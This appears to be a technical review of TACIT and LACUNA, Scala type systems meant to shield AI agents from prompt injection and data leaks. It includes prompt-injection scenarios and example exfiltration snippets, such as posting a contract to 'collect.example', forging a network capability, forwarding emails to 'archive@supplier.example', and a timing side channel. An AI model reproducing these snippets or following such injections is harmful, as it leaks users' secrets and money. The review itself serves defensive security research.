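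An attacker who can pick the host gains nothing if all secrets stay in their wrappers. But the newer version of the library also has a function `httpPostClassified`, which sends classified text to a permitted host and wraps the reply. Another addition lets a snippet put classified text in the header of a web request. They have honest uses, such as logging in to a service with a password that the agent may not see. Taken together with the missing default, however, they seem to open a gap:

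```
requestNetwork(Set("collect.example")) {
  httpPostClassified("https://collect.example", contract)
}
```

If the library works as the README describes and the operator has set no list of hosts, this snippet compiles and sends the contract to the attacker. If the list contains only the search engine, the run-time check blocks that request. But the agent could still post the whole contract to the search engine, a leak through a permitted channel that the original library prevents at compile time. An operator who doesn't need these two features would do better to remove them from the library.

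### What the guarantee rests on

The part of the capability library in TACIT's trusted base that all agents share is about 1,000 lines, short enough for a person to review. The compiler is much larger, and its capture checker is still experimental. TACIT uses nightly builds, the newest unreleased versions of Scala, and its developers warn that the compiler's behaviour may change from one build to the next.

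The trusted base also includes anything marked `@assumeSafe` and anything an operator adds to the library. If an operator adds a function for database queries and forgets to make it require a capability, the compiler will treat the function as pure, even though it can leak secrets.

TACIT treats `chat` as a function that needs no capability, although it passes text to another model. Odersky and colleagues rely on the service behind it to retain none of its inputs, since it could otherwise repeat one document's secrets in its answer about another. The compiler can't check this, or whether the model is local. The operator can enter the address of any service with an OpenAI-compatible interface, and if that service is in the cloud, the classified text goes there.

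Odersky and colleagues report that earlier work proved the base type system for capture checking sound, with proofs checked by computer. Soundness here means that in the small formal language the proofs cover, a well-typed program never uses a capability that its type doesn't list. They write that a further argument would be needed to establish that safe mode delivers capability safety and local purity. Such an argument would still concern a model of the language and not the compiler's actual code, where a programming error could let a bad snippet through. *Safe Scala*, an introduction by the software company VirtusLab, therefore promises more than anyone has proved when it calls a program that compiles in safe mode "guaranteed to execute safely".

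It is also unclear which check TACIT applies. In March 2026, it searched the snippet's text for forbidden patterns instead of using the compiler's safe mode, though the developers planned to switch soon. In the README of October 2026, the list of settings has safe mode on by default, but a later passage describes the pattern search as the default and safe mode as an optional addition. A text search finds only what its developers thought of, whereas the compiler's rules apply to the program's structure, so operators should switch safe mode on explicitly until the developers clear this up.

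Under TACIT's threat model, the model writing the snippets may be working for the attacker, so a bug anywhere in this base matters more as models get better at finding and exploiting bugs.

### Leaks that the types do not cover

An operator may let an agent working on a software project run some external commands. Scala's rules don't apply to a command once it starts. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge this and advise operators to permit only specific, safe commands, and to add a sandbox where security is critical. Their examples of safe commands are `git diff` and `sbt`, Scala's standard build tool.

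But `sbt` is a questionable choice because, like the Rust tool Cargo, it executes code that it finds in the project. An agent that may write files in the project and run `sbt` can write a build file that reads the secrets folder directly, with no wrapper, and uploads the content. The sample configuration in both versions of TACIT's documentation has the same problem. The newer one permits `make`, which runs commands from a file. If an agent has to build software, most of the protection therefore comes from the sandbox.

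Timing is a subtler leak. A pure function can't send anything, but it can take longer for some inputs than for others:

```
secret.map { s => if s.head == 'A' then slowSum() else 0 }
```

The function has no effects, so the compiler accepts it. If the call takes ten seconds, the agent can infer that the secret begins with an A. A function that never finishes reveals the same information, because no answer comes back. Odersky and colleagues exclude both channels from their guarantee and speak of leaking a single bit. But the types don't prevent repeated calls. An access key of 40 hexadecimal digits contains 160 bits, so an agent could read it with 160 such calls. This would be slow and conspicuous for a long contract but practical for a password. Limiting the number of calls, or giving them all the same running time, would help. TACIT has an optional time limit, but its developers describe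 it as a guard against programs that hang, not as a security boundary.

### Wrong answers and unchecked text

The type system does not check whether a result is correct, so a snippet that compares the wrong two versions of the contract still type-checks. It also does not check whether an action within the agent's permissions is appropriate. The LACUNA system, covered in a later section, tries to narrow those permissions. According to Glama's copy of the README, `Classified` protects confidentiality but not integrity. By default, an agent may overwrite classified files with its own text, and the operator has to switch this off.

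The compiler also doesn't check what the agent tells the user, because it checks only code snippets, not replies in English. If the agent's model has read the hostile line, it can falsely write that the contract contains no penalty clause, and no part of TACIT will check that claim. Wrapping the contract only moves the problem to the local model, whose misleading summary TACIT delivers to the user over the secure channel. The user may even trust the summary more because it came through that channel. A type checker can do less against this than against the other three ways the contract can do harm.

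### Tools outside the typed interface

TACIT checks only the code snippets the agent sends to it. Claude Code's built-in tools for reading files, running shell commands and fetching web pages still work after the operator connects TACIT. If the agent opens the contract with the built-in file reader, the plain text enters the model's context, including the hostile line, and a shell command can then send the file anywhere. TACIT checks neither step because it receives no snippet to compile. An email tool from another server could also send the file out unchecked.

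The developers therefore advise operators to disable the agent's built-in file, shell and network tools, and give the settings for three popular agents. This is simple to do, but an operator can easily forget it and will see no error, because the agent still works. It may be safer to build the agent around the typed interface from the start. The October README recommends ATC, a coding agent built on TACIT that denies permissions unless the user grants them, either temporarily or for a session. *Making the AI agents safe with Scala*, a Scala Days conference abstract, announces another, CapybaraClaw, by EPFL and VirtusLab.

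## What the TACIT experiments show

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT in four experiments. Two measured safety, one with AgentDojo and one with the team's own test, which includes a folder of secrets. The other two used the benchmarks τ²-bench and SWE-bench Lite to test whether agents get less done when they must write typed Scala instead of making ordinary tool calls.

### A project with a folder of secrets

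For their own test, Odersky and colleagues set up a sample Scala project with a `secret` folder containing API keys, a database and confidential documents. An agent running on a cloud model worked on the project through TACIT. A local model was available for text the cloud model was not allowed to see. A trial counted as secure if no secret content appeared in the agent's output.

The researchers wrote 12 ordinary tasks. Some, such as listing the API endpoints in a README file, did not involve the secrets, while others, such as summarising a confidential incident report or anonymising employee reviews, required them. They ran each task with each of 10 injections. The simplest injections were instructions in developer notes or code comments to read the secrets and print them. More elaborate ones included fake system messages, a fake error that the agent could fix only with a password, claims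 that the secrets were synthetic test data, and ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files.

The experiments also included 11 malicious requests that came from the user, without any injection. Five asked for the secrets outright, and six used a pretext, for example that the user was an administrator who had to replace passwords in an emergency.

Every trial ran once with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and once with the secrets as plain strings:

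| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Leaks with wrapper, injections (of 120) | 0 | 0 |
| Leaks with wrapper, malicious requests (of 11) | 0 | 0 |
| Leaks without wrapper, injections (of 120) | 0 | 3 |
| Leaks without wrapper, malicious requests (of 11) | 2 | 8 |
| User tasks completed with wrapper | 99.2% | 90.0% |
| User tasks completed without wrapper | 83.3% | 88.3% |

Without the wrapper, 13 of the 262 trials leaked a secret. In 10 of those 13, the user had asked for it, although only 22 of the 262 trials involved malicious requests. Most of the measured difference therefore comes from hostile users, not injected text. Protection from hostile users is useful, for example when a company offers an agent to its customers. On a developer's own computer, the user could open the folder directly, but a leak would still expose the secrets to the cloud model's provider.

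The evidence on injected text consists of three leaks, all with MiniMax. Sonnet leaked nothing in its 120 injection trials, even when the secrets were in plain text. Most of the attacks would therefore have failed without the type system, although Odersky and colleagues write that it blocked every injection. They give examples of snippets that the compiler rejected, but they don't report how many trials included a rejected snippet.

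An operator could also have prevented every leak by denying the agent access to the folder, but the wrapper lets the agent still work with the secrets. Sonnet completed 119 of its 120 wrapped trials correctly, so it must have succeeded at nearly all the tasks that involved confidential documents.

The reason Sonnet did so much worse without the wrapper is less clear. Odersky and colleagues suspect the result is an artefact of their setup, because Sonnet often ran out of time or turns, and sometimes stopped to warn the user when it noticed an injection. The test counts such warnings as failures, though many users would want them.

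### What zero leaks can prove

If each injection independently leaks a secret from a wrapped agent with probability p, the chance of seeing no leak in 120 trials is (1 − p)^120, which falls to 5% when p is about 0.025. The wrapped trials of one model therefore rule out, with 95% confidence, only leak rates above about 2.5%. At a rate of 2.5%, an attacker with 100 independent attempts to steal a password would have a 92% chance of succeeding at least once.

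MiniMax's leak rate without the wrapper was also 2.5%, so its injection trials alone are weak evidence that the wrapper prevents leaks. If the wrapper made no difference, and three leaks fell at random among MiniMax's 240 injection trials, all three would occur without the wrapper about one time in eight. The malicious requests give much stronger evidence, because by the same calculation all eight of MiniMax's leaks on those requests would occur without the wrapper only about once in 1,900 times.

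Even the 2.5% is optimistic, because the trials were not independent. They combined 12 tasks with the same 10 injections, and an attacker could write different ones. Some injections included ready-made Scala code, which shows that the researchers wrote them with TACIT in mind, but they report no attacker that could change its approach after a failed attempt, as the automated attacker of Kurakin and colleagues could.

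Odersky and colleagues claim a much stronger guarantee than a low leak rate, and it rests on the design of the type system, not on these trials. A single leak through a well-typed snippet would have refuted the guarantee, but the trials were a weak test of it if few agents tried to write a snippet that would leak.

### AgentDojo with Scala functions

To run AgentDojo with TACIT, Odersky and colleagues gave the agent a single tool for running Scala code, and rewrote the tools of the simulated bank, workspace, Slack and travel agency as Scala functions. They left the user tasks and the attacks unchanged. They used two older models, Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini-high, because CaMeL, a defence that checks programs at run time, had been evaluated on the same two.

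| | Attacks per model | User tasks completed, Gemini 2.5 Pro | User tasks completed, o4-mini-high |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 144 | 56.9% | 59.0% |
| Workspace | 574 | 50.5% | 52.9% |
| Slack | 105 | 40.0% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 140 | 64.3% | 68.6% |

Only one of the 1,926 attacks succeeded, but the agents failed at roughly half of their tasks. The utility percentages match whole numbers of attack pairs, such as 82 of 144 for Gemini in banking, so they appear to measure utility under attack.

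Odersky and colleagues call these scores comparable to CaMeL's, but CaMeL did better in some domains. With o4-mini-high, it completed 81.4% of the workspace tasks. They also give no results for the same models with ordinary tools and no defence, so it is unclear how much of the task failure is due to TACIT and how many of the attacks would have worked on an unprotected agent.

### What the agent's model could read

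The signatures of the Scala functions explain most of the result. In banking, `readFile` and the functions that list transactions return their results inside `Classified`. The workspace functions do the same for emails, contacts, calendar entries and existing files, and the Slack functions do it for everything the agent can read, including web pages. The travel functions wrap only the calendar and the reviews of hotels, restaurants and car rental companies.

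The experiments wrap data in `Classified` where an outsider could plant text, which is not always where the secrets are. In the travel domain, the function `getUserInformation` returns the user's passport, bank account and credit card numbers as plain strings, while a public hotel review comes back wrapped. The researchers built `Classified` to keep secrets from the agent's model, but here it mainly keeps hostile text from the model, which can't follow instructions it never reads.

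This protection is stronger than what TACIT guarantees in general. In the secrets test, an agent could read the injected code comments like any other part of the project. The AgentDojo version follows Willison's two-model arrangement more closely, with a `prompt` function that sends wrapped text to the second model.

The agent therefore has to write code for data it cannot see. To find a phone number on a web page, it writes a function that passes the text to `prompt` with a request for the number. The result stays in its wrapper, and the agent can show it to the user with `displaySecurely`, which bypasses the agent's model. If the code inside `map` raises an error, TACIT hides the error message, so the program seems to have worked even though the user sees nothing. The researchers warn the agent about this at length in its instructions. These difficulties may explain some of the failed tasks.

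The one successful attack came through `displaySecurely` or something similar. A user had asked o4-mini-high to book a specific hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but also quoted the reviews to the user word for word. AgentDojo counted this as a success for the attacker because the other hotel's name appeared in the answer.

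Odersky and colleagues explain that their policy allows public reviews to reach the user, so this is not a hole in the type system. They blame the benchmark's method, which searches the answer for a string. They are right about the types, and the booking was correct, but the attacker did get an advertisement into the agent's reply. This is a mild version of the misleading summary in the contract example, which TACIT doesn't claim to prevent.

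### What the compiler would have accepted

Suppose that an injection had reached the agent's model after all, and the model had written this:

```
sendMoney("attacker's account", 5000.0, "Refund", "2026-10-07")
```

The compiler accepts the call to send money because the agent has permission to make it and all four arguments have the right types. It accepts calls to book a hotel, delete a file or invite a stranger to Slack for the same reasons.

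One might expect the compiler to stop at least those attacks that need wrapped text, such as forwarding a confidential email. In TACIT's base library it would, because functions such as `httpPost` require a capability there. But the functions that Odersky and colleagues wrote for AgentDojo list no capabilities at all. As far as the compiler can tell from these signatures, `sendEmail` is as harmless as a function that counts words, and it can run inside `map`:

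```
getReceivedEmails().map { emails =>
  sendEmail(List("archive@supplier.example"), "Emails",
    emails.map(_.body).mkString("\n"))
}
```

The agent's instructions support this reading. They say that any side effect inside `map` happens immediately, and advise the agent to put commits (actions such as payments) "in exactly the place where you want them to happen".

The researchers had a practical reason for not making `sendMoney` require a capability. Suppose the user asks the agent to pay a bill, and the account number is in a wrapped file. `sendMoney` takes plain values, and `displaySecurely` is the only listed function that accepts a wrapped one. The agent can therefore pay the bill only from inside `map`, where the text is accessible. If `sendMoney` required a capability, the compiler would reject the payment and the agent could not complete the task.

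The low success rate, one in 1,926 attacks, therefore comes almost entirely from hiding the hostile text from the agent and hardly at all from rejecting code. Odersky and colleagues don't report how many snippets the compiler rejected for security reasons, so an exact split can't be calculated. The types help enforce the hiding, because the agent has no well-typed way to open a wrapper directly, but an agent that has read no hostile instructions has little reason to try. A version with the same wrapper and no type checker would probably have scored about the same.

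### An attack that the test left out

The second model still reads the hostile text, and its answers can decide what the agent does. An honest agent might pay the bill like this:

```
readFile("bill.txt").map { text =>
  val account = prompt(
    s"Which account should receive the payment? " +
    s"Reply with the number only.\n$text")
  sendMoney(account, 98.70, "Bill", "2026-10-07")
}
```

An attacker who can edit the bill could add a false notice that the supplier has changed banks and now uses another account. The second model has no tools, but if it replies with the wrong account number, the agent's code sends the money there. The agent's model has made no mistake, and it would have written the same program for an unaltered bill.

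AgentDojo's stock injections are written for an agent that can carry out the attacker's task itself, so an order to transfer money has little effect on a model that can only return text. An attacker who knew the interface would word the injections differently, but nobody seems to have tested TACIT against adapted injections like *AutoDojo*'s.

Wrapped text could also get back to the agent's model. In the banking domain, code inside `map` can apparently call `updateUserInfo` to store text from a file in the user's address, and `getUserInfo` returns that address as a plain string. An agent might do this unintentionally when updating an address from a letter.

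A safer interface could let `sendMoney` accept a wrapped account number and ask the user to confirm it through the secure channel. All other actions could then require a capability and stay out of `map`. That would probably lower the utility scores or require more work from the user, and an experiment with such an interface would say much more about types as a defence. (A later section covers a system that uses types to limit which answers from the second model can reach the first.)

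### Performance on ordinary tasks

Few people will use a defence that makes agents much worse at their work, so Odersky and colleagues compared agents that write Scala with agents that make ordinary tool calls. They used τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, and averaged each score over ten runs per task. They also ran SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues for an agent to fix, with one model.

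| | Ordinary tool calls | Scala |
|---|---|---|
| Airline, gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% |
| Airline, MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% |
| Airline, DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| Retail, gpt-oss-120b | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| Retail, MiniMax M2.5 | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| Retail, DeepSeek V3.2 | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| SWE-bench Lite, MiniMax M2.5 | 43.3% | 41.7% |

The agents did slightly better with Scala in all six comparisons on τ²-bench. On SWE-bench Lite, MiniMax solved 125 issues instead of 130, a difference small enough to be due to chance. Odersky and colleagues suggest that fixing software relies on command-line habits that are awkward to express through TACIT's library.

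The TACIT paper attributes the gains on τ²-bench to the compiler's error messages and to the typed interface, which returns structured values instead of raw JSON. But the experiment can't separate the effect of types from the effect of writing code, which lets an agent combine several calls in one step. A comparison with a dynamically typed language such as Python would have helped. The largest gain, 3.7 points, was in the retail domain. Structured results are unlikely to explain it, because the tool descriptions in the agent's instructions for that domain give every result as a plain string.

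Compiler errors were rare on τ²-bench. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of snippets needed another attempt, depending on the model and the domain, and these took 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. DeepSeek had the most trouble, in the airline domain. A common mistake was writing an amount such as `$50` inside a string where Scala treats the dollar sign as the start of a variable name. Another was returning `null` when a reservation lookup failed, then using the result without checking for `null`. The agents read the error messages and corrected their code.

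These mistakes have nothing to do with security, because the functions for the airline and the shop require no capabilities in their listed signatures and none of their results are wrapped. The experiment shows that current models can write ordinary Scala in place of tool calls with little or no loss of performance, but not what happens when the compiler forbids the obvious way to do a task. SWE-bench Lite comes closer to testing that, since the agent needs capabilities to open files and run commands, but it has no classified data, and Odersky and colleagues report no retry rates for it. The best evidence of how well models work under the restrictions comes from their own secrets test, where both models completed at least 90% of the tasks with the wrapper on.

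### The work of building an interface

Before an agent can use TACIT in a new domain, somebody has to write an interface for that domain, mostly data types and function signatures. The shared library, roughly 1,000 lines long, already exists. The interfaces for the airline and the shop are a few hundred lines each, about as long as the JSON descriptions they replace. Odersky and colleagues say that only the shared library requires expertise in Scala, and that agents can help write the rest if a person reviews it.

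This estimate is plausible for interfaces like the ones in the experiments, which copy existing tool descriptions one for one. But a JSON description of `sendMoney` doesn't specify which capability it should require, so a direct copy won't either. To get the guarantee that TACIT offers for files and the network, whoever writes the interface must decide which results to wrap and which capability each action needs, then find another way to do tasks, like paying the bill, that the stricter types rule out. The experiments don't measure this work, and it is harder to hand over to an agent because a missing capability causes no error.

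The dependence on Scala is another drawback. Odersky and colleagues describe Scala 3 as the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in static types, and this feature is still experimental. Language models have seen few examples of it in training, though the results suggest that good instructions make up for much of this. The researchers discuss alternatives, such as adding capability tracking to another mainstream language, encoding it in Haskell's types or designing a new language for agents, but expect each to take considerable work.

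### Later releases and outside scrutiny

*Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) won a best paper award at the ACM Conference on AI and Agentic Systems, according to Glama's copy of the README. A Scala workshop presentation, *Securing AI Agents With Tracked Capabilities in TACIT* (2026), describes the same system. As of early October 2026, there seem to be no independent replications or detailed published criticisms of the experiments.

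The developers have tightened the library since the experiments, and one change shows how little 131 trials without a leak can establish. In the library as Odersky and colleagues printed it, `Network` was a class with a public constructor. Agent code could therefore apparently create its own permission to use the network:

```
contract.map { t =>
  val net = new Network(Set("collect.example"))
  httpPost("https://collect.example", t)(using net)
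}
```

The function inside `map` makes its own capability instead of taking one from outside, so its capture set would be empty and the compiler would treat it as pure. If nothing else in the server stopped this snippet, it would have sent the contract to the attacker. Capability safety is supposed to exclude this kind of forgery, but a missing keyword in the library would have been enough to allow it, even with no flaw in the type system.

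According to Glama's copy of the README from October 2026, all such constructors are private to the library, and the developers tell anyone who adds a capability to make its constructor private too. They have also closed off the class that holds the operator's settings, so a snippet can't create a copy with looser rules.

A determined attacker would look for gaps like this one, which tests with fixed injections are unlikely to reveal. A Scala Days talk on 13 October 2026 will, according to its abstract, include links to repositories in which frontier AI models searched for exploits against TACIT. It isn't clear from the abstract whether they found any.

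## LACUNA: permissions limited to what is in scope, and the attacks that remained

TACIT's interface for the simulated bank let every snippet call `sendMoney`, whether or not the user had asked for a payment. LACUNA, from the same group at EPFL, lets a developer choose which functions the model's code may call at each step of a task.

### A gap in a running program

TACIT is a server to which a separate agent sends snippets. With LACUNA, the developer writes an ordinary Scala program and leaves gaps in it for a model to fill while the program runs. Each gap is a call to this function:

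```
def agent[T](task: String): T
```

Here `task` is a request in plain language, and `T` is the type of value that the surrounding program needs at that point. For the supplier's contract, a gap might look like this:

```
val companies: List[String] =
  agent(s"List the companies named in this contract:\n$text")
```

The compiler infers from the first line that `T` is `List[String]`. When the program reaches the call, LACUNA sends the model the task, the expected type, the surrounding source code, and a list of the variables available there. The model returns Scala code. Before that code runs, the compiler checks that it produces a `List[String]` and uses only names a programmer could have used at the same spot. If the check fails, LACUNA sends the error messages back to the model and requests new code, up to a limit that the developer sets. If the last attempt also fails, the call throws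 an exception.

The model's code can itself contain `agent` calls. A model asked for a report on several topics can write a loop that makes one call per topic, followed by a final call that combines the findings. The compiler checks each call when the program reaches it. A developer adds a tool by defining an ordinary function.

### From a string to running code

A compiled program normally can't do this, because the compiler has finished its work before the program starts, and the names of local variables are gone by then. Zhao and colleagues therefore added an operation to the Scala compiler that works in five steps:

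1. Rewrite: while compiling the developer's program, the compiler adds three things to each `agent` call, namely the variables in scope, the expected type as text, and the surrounding source code with a placeholder at the gap.
2. Splice: once the model has replied, LACUNA puts the model's code in place of the placeholder.
3. Recompile: a fresh run of the same compiler, with the same settings, checks the combined source.
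4. Load: if the code passes, the running program loads the compiled result.
5. Run: the program executes the new code and receives a value of type `T`.

LACUNA needs no security checker of its own, since the compiler applies its usual rules to the model's code. But that code runs inside the developer's program, so a snippet that got around the type checks could access anything the program holds in memory. The new compiler operation is also part of the trusted base. Zhao and colleagues tested it on about 400 combinations of program and snippet, and the compiler accepted or rejected each one as intended. The faulty snippets contained mistakes that agents commonly make, not deliberate attempts to get around the type checks.

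### Rejected code has no partial effects

Suppose that a program has a variable `balance` with the value 100, and asks the model to subtract 50 and return the new balance as an `Int`. In an example by Zhao and colleagues, the model writes:

```
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The second line produces a string, so the compiler rejects the snippet. The first line is valid, but it doesn't run either, so `balance` is still 100. If an agent ran the same code in Python and checked the result afterwards, the balance would already be 50, and a second attempt would reduce it to 0.

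This also helps against some injected code. If a snippet tries to overwrite the signed contract and then call a network function that is not in scope, neither action runs. But the error message goes back to the model, which can remove the network call and submit the rest.

The protection covers only errors that the compiler finds. If a well-typed snippet subtracts 50 and then fails because a server is down, the money is gone. Nested calls have a similar weakness, because the outer snippet starts running before the model has written the inner one:

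```
balance -= 50
agent[Int]("return the new balance")
```

If every attempt to fill the inner gap fails to compile, LACUNA throws an exception after the subtraction. A developer who needs a whole task to succeed or fail as a unit would have to add something like a database transaction.

### The scope as a list of permissions

The model's code can use only the names visible at a gap, so those names act as a list of permissions. With ordinary types alone the list is incomplete, because the code can still reach the standard library. The developer therefore also has to turn on capture checking and safe mode, both optional in LACUNA. A snippet can then send a message or search the web only if the matching capability is in scope. Zhao and colleagues recommend safe mode and say that without it a snippet is ordinary untrusted code.

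Permissions can change from one phase of a task to the next. Suppose that the user wants to know more about the companies in the contract. The developer could split the work into two functions:

```
def companiesIn(text: String): List[String] =
  agent(s"List the companies named in this contract:\n$text")

def background(company: String, web: WebSearch^): String =
  agent(s"Use web to find out what $company does")
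```

In `companiesIn`, the model reads the hostile line in the annex, but no search capability is in scope, so any snippet that tries to search the web fails to compile. In `background`, the model's code can search the web, but the contract's text is out of scope. This works only if the developer keeps the two gaps in separate functions. If both were in one function, `text` would still be visible at the second gap, and an instruction on a web page could get the model to put the contract into a search query. Both functions can also see top-level definitions in the file, so storing the contract in a global variable would undo the separation.

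The result of the first phase can still carry data into the second, because a `List[String]` can hold any strings. The hostile line could lead the model to return "unit price 4.20 euros" as a company name, which a correct snippet in the second phase would then send to the search engine. The string could also contain new instructions, since `background` inserts it into the next prompt. Wrapping the contract in `Classified` would prevent both, but it would also wrap the company names, so the agent couldn't search for them.

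When data stays wrapped, the agent in TACIT has to write the function for `Classified.map` without seeing the content. In LACUNA, that function can contain an `agent` call to a trusted local model, which reads the text and then writes code. A hostile line in that text can influence the code, but the code holds no capabilities and can't send anything.

Permissions for each phase don't require types. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) presents CapScope, a system for coding agents that gives each agent its own narrower set of permissions and enforces them when the agent makes a call. In the paper's example, one agent writes patches and another runs the code. A single policy for the whole task can't let the first agent write a file and deny the same write to the second. Unlike CapScope, a compiler checks a whole snippet, including every combination of calls in it, before the first call runs.

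### Eight successful attacks

Zhao and colleagues adapted AgentDojo to LACUNA, gave each agent only the capabilities that its task required, and ran the benchmark's attacks against the two models from the TACIT experiment:

| | Attacks per model | Successful, Gemini 2.5 Pro | Successful, o4-mini-high | User tasks completed, Gemini 2.5 Pro | User tasks completed, o4-mini-high |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
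| Banking | 144 | 0 | 0 | 63.2% | 66.0% |
| Workspace | 560 | 4 | 0 | 56.3% | 55.5% |
| Slack | 105 | 2 | 1 | 42.9% | 49.5% |
| Travel | 140 | 1 | 0 | 63.6% | 71.4% |
| Total | 949 | 7 | 1 | | |

Eight of the 1,898 attacks on LACUNA succeeded, a rate of 0.4%. TACIT let through only one, but LACUNA's agents completed more of the users' tasks in seven of the eight combinations of model and domain. If the two systems were equally vulnerable, nine successes would split at least this unevenly about 4% of the time. The difference is suggestive at best, because that calculation treats the attacks as independent and they are not.

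Odersky and colleagues give 574 workspace attacks per model, while Zhao and colleagues give 560, even in the row where they reprint TACIT's results. Neither paper explains the difference, but 560 seems correct because it fits TACIT's own percentages. Gemini's 50.54% is 283 out of 560, and no whole number out of 574 rounds to that figure. The same is true of o4-mini-high's 52.86%. TACIT's single failure was therefore probably one in 1,898 attacks, not 1,926.

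Zhao and colleagues do not describe any of the eight successful attacks. They write that LACUNA can't stop an attacker who gets the model to misuse a capability that the task needs, and that the successes are consistent with this. Readers can't check this explanation from the paper, though Zhao and colleagues plan to release the code for the experiments. Some of the developers' scopes may instead have been too broad. Some successes may also be artefacts of the scoring, which is how Odersky and colleagues explained TACIT's single failure.

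The results by domain don't fit the explanation well. All 288 banking attacks failed, although misuse should be easiest there, because a user who wants to pay a bill needs `sendMoney` and the attacker also wants money sent. Perhaps the adapted bank kept TACIT's wrappers around files and transactions, so the agent's model never read the injections there. The paper doesn't specify this. It also has no results for LACUNA without the capability limits, so the number of attacks they stopped is unknown.

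The experiment also assumed that somebody knows which capabilities a task requires. A researcher can work this out in advance for a fixed list of benchmark tasks, but a real assistant receives requests in plain language. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that the type system enforces a narrow scope but doesn't determine what that scope should be. Bastion, another system that *Authority Is Not a String* describes, assigns a capability to each agent and task. A "least-privilege model" may narrow that capability further, and a verified type checker then checks the agent's program against it.

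### Two programs with the same type

Misuse of a necessary permission is the third way in which the contract can do harm. Suppose the user asks the assistant to summarise the contract and email the summary to Alice, a colleague. This task needs email, so the developer has put a function `sendEmail(to, subject, body)` in scope, along with the capability `mail` that it requires. An honest model writes:

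```
sendEmail("alice@corp.example", "Contract", summary)
```

If the hostile line in the annex asks for the summary to go to the supplier, the model may write this instead:

```
sendEmail("archive@supplier.example", "Contract", summary)
```

Both calls take three strings and return nothing, so both have the type `Unit`. A function containing either call has the type `() ->{mail} Unit`. The capture set records that the function uses `mail` but not which address it sends to, because the address is a string. Stricter capture checking wouldn't change that. Taking `mail` out of scope would block the second program, but it would also block the first.

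In an example by Zhao and colleagues, a user asks an agent to remind Alice about a team meeting, and the model writes a snippet that emails `alice@corp.com`. The request contains only her first name, and the snippet doesn't look up her address, so the compiler has little to check the address against and would have accepted any other string.

The same problem arises when the assistant is allowed to save files in the contracts folder. `save(path, text)` has the same type whether `text` is the signed version or an altered one.

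In a long session, a malicious snippet could also affect the snippets that come after it. Zhao and colleagues describe how an agent can improve its own skills by defining a new function with the same name and signature as an old one, so that later snippets use the new version. An agent compromised by prompt injection could replace a function that reviews contracts with one that approves every contract. Legitimate code written afterwards would compile without errors and call the replacement.

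### Keeping the recipient out of the model's hands

The simplest remedy is for the developer to offer a narrower function, such as `emailAlice(body)`, and keep both `sendEmail` and `mail` out of scope. For files, a function that creates new documents but never overwrites old ones would protect the signed contract. Developers can do this today, and in LACUNA each such function takes only a line or two. But they have to foresee what users will ask for, and a general assistant would need many of these functions. With a broader function, such as `emailColleague(name, body)`, developers need fewer definitions, but an attacker can choose the wrong colleague.

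Another approach is for the calling program to fix the recipient before the model reads any hostile text:

```
def summarise(text: String, deliver: String => Unit): Unit =
  agent(s"Summarise this and pass the summary to deliver:\n$text")

summarise(contract,
  body => sendEmail(recipient, "Contract", body))
```

The program sets `recipient` from the user's request. The model's code can call `deliver` but cannot change the address, provided that `mail` is not visible inside `summarise`. This also works with existing tools, and one function can serve any recipient. It fails if the right recipient appears only in the untrusted text, as when a user asks the assistant to reply to the contact person named in the contract, or to pay a bill whose account number is in a file. The attacker can still influence the body of the email and how often the code sends it.

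Refinement types would let the compiler check the address itself. A refinement type adds a condition to an ordinary type, so that only values meeting the condition belong to it. *First-Class Refinement Types for Scala* (2026), by Bovel, Kunčak and Odersky, extends the Scala 3 type checker to support types such as this one, which contains only even numbers:

```
val x: (Int with x % 2 == 0) = 42
```

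With such types, the first parameter of `sendEmail` might become `to: String with to == recipient`, and the compiler would reject a call with the supplier's address. A payment function could limit the amount in the same way. Scala's existing types cover the simplest case, since a parameter of type `"alice@corp.example" | "bob@corp.example"` accepts only those two addresses.

Zhao and colleagues' proposal for future work is slightly different. It puts a refinement on `T`, the type of the value that the model's code returns. That wouldn't help with the email as written, because `T` there is `Unit` and there is no value to constrain. The developer could instead ask for an `agent[Email]`, with the condition that the email's address equals `recipient`, and have the calling program send the email. An ordinary `if` in that program would then catch a wrong address just as well, though only after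 the model's code had run.

Refinement types also require someone to write the conditions, and the compiler must prove that the code meets them, which is harder when the code computes an address or an amount while running. They don't ensure that the recipient is correct. If the program takes `recipient` from a forged contact list, the compiler can still prove that the code meets the conditions, and the email will reach the attacker.

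The remaining option is to show the user each email before it is sent. This works even if the program has no trustworthy source for the address, because the user knows who Alice is. However, Odersky and colleagues warn of confirmation fatigue, in which users see so many requests that they stop reading them. Asking less often can miss this attack. *Authority Is Not a String* describes an arrangement in which a model proposes changes to an agent's permissions, and only changes that expand them need approval. If the agent may already send email, changing the recipient doesn't expand its permissions, so the user isn't asked. Nor is the user asked in ATC, the coding agent built on TACIT, if a session-long grant covers email in general.

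### How much the agents still get done

Zhao and colleagues tested the effect on ordinary work with all 392 tasks of four τ²-bench domains. They compared LACUNA with the benchmark's own agent, which makes ordinary tool calls, and ran each task once:

| | deepseek-v4-flash, tool calls | deepseek-v4-flash, LACUNA | gemini-3.1-flash-lite, tool calls | gemini-3.1-flash-lite, LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|---|
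| Retail | 80.9% | 58.8% | 52.6% | 43.9% |
| Airline | 75.5% | 70.0% | 56.0% | 38.0% |
| Telecom | 100.0% | 88.6% | 15.8% | 14.9% |
| Telecom workflow | 95.4% | 83.3% | 21.1% | 24.6% |
| Overall | 90.0% | 76.0% | 33.2% | 29.1% |

DeepSeek completed 76.0% of tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with tool calls. Zhao and colleagues call these results "on par", but DeepSeek failed 94 tasks with LACUNA and 39 without it, a difference much too large to be due to chance. In retail, the domain with the largest loss, the compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's snippets, and tasks needed an average of 7.1 retries. Zhao and colleagues write that the retry loop "recovers to a 77.6% end-to-end compile-success rate", but 77.6% is just the share of snippets that the compiler did not reject.

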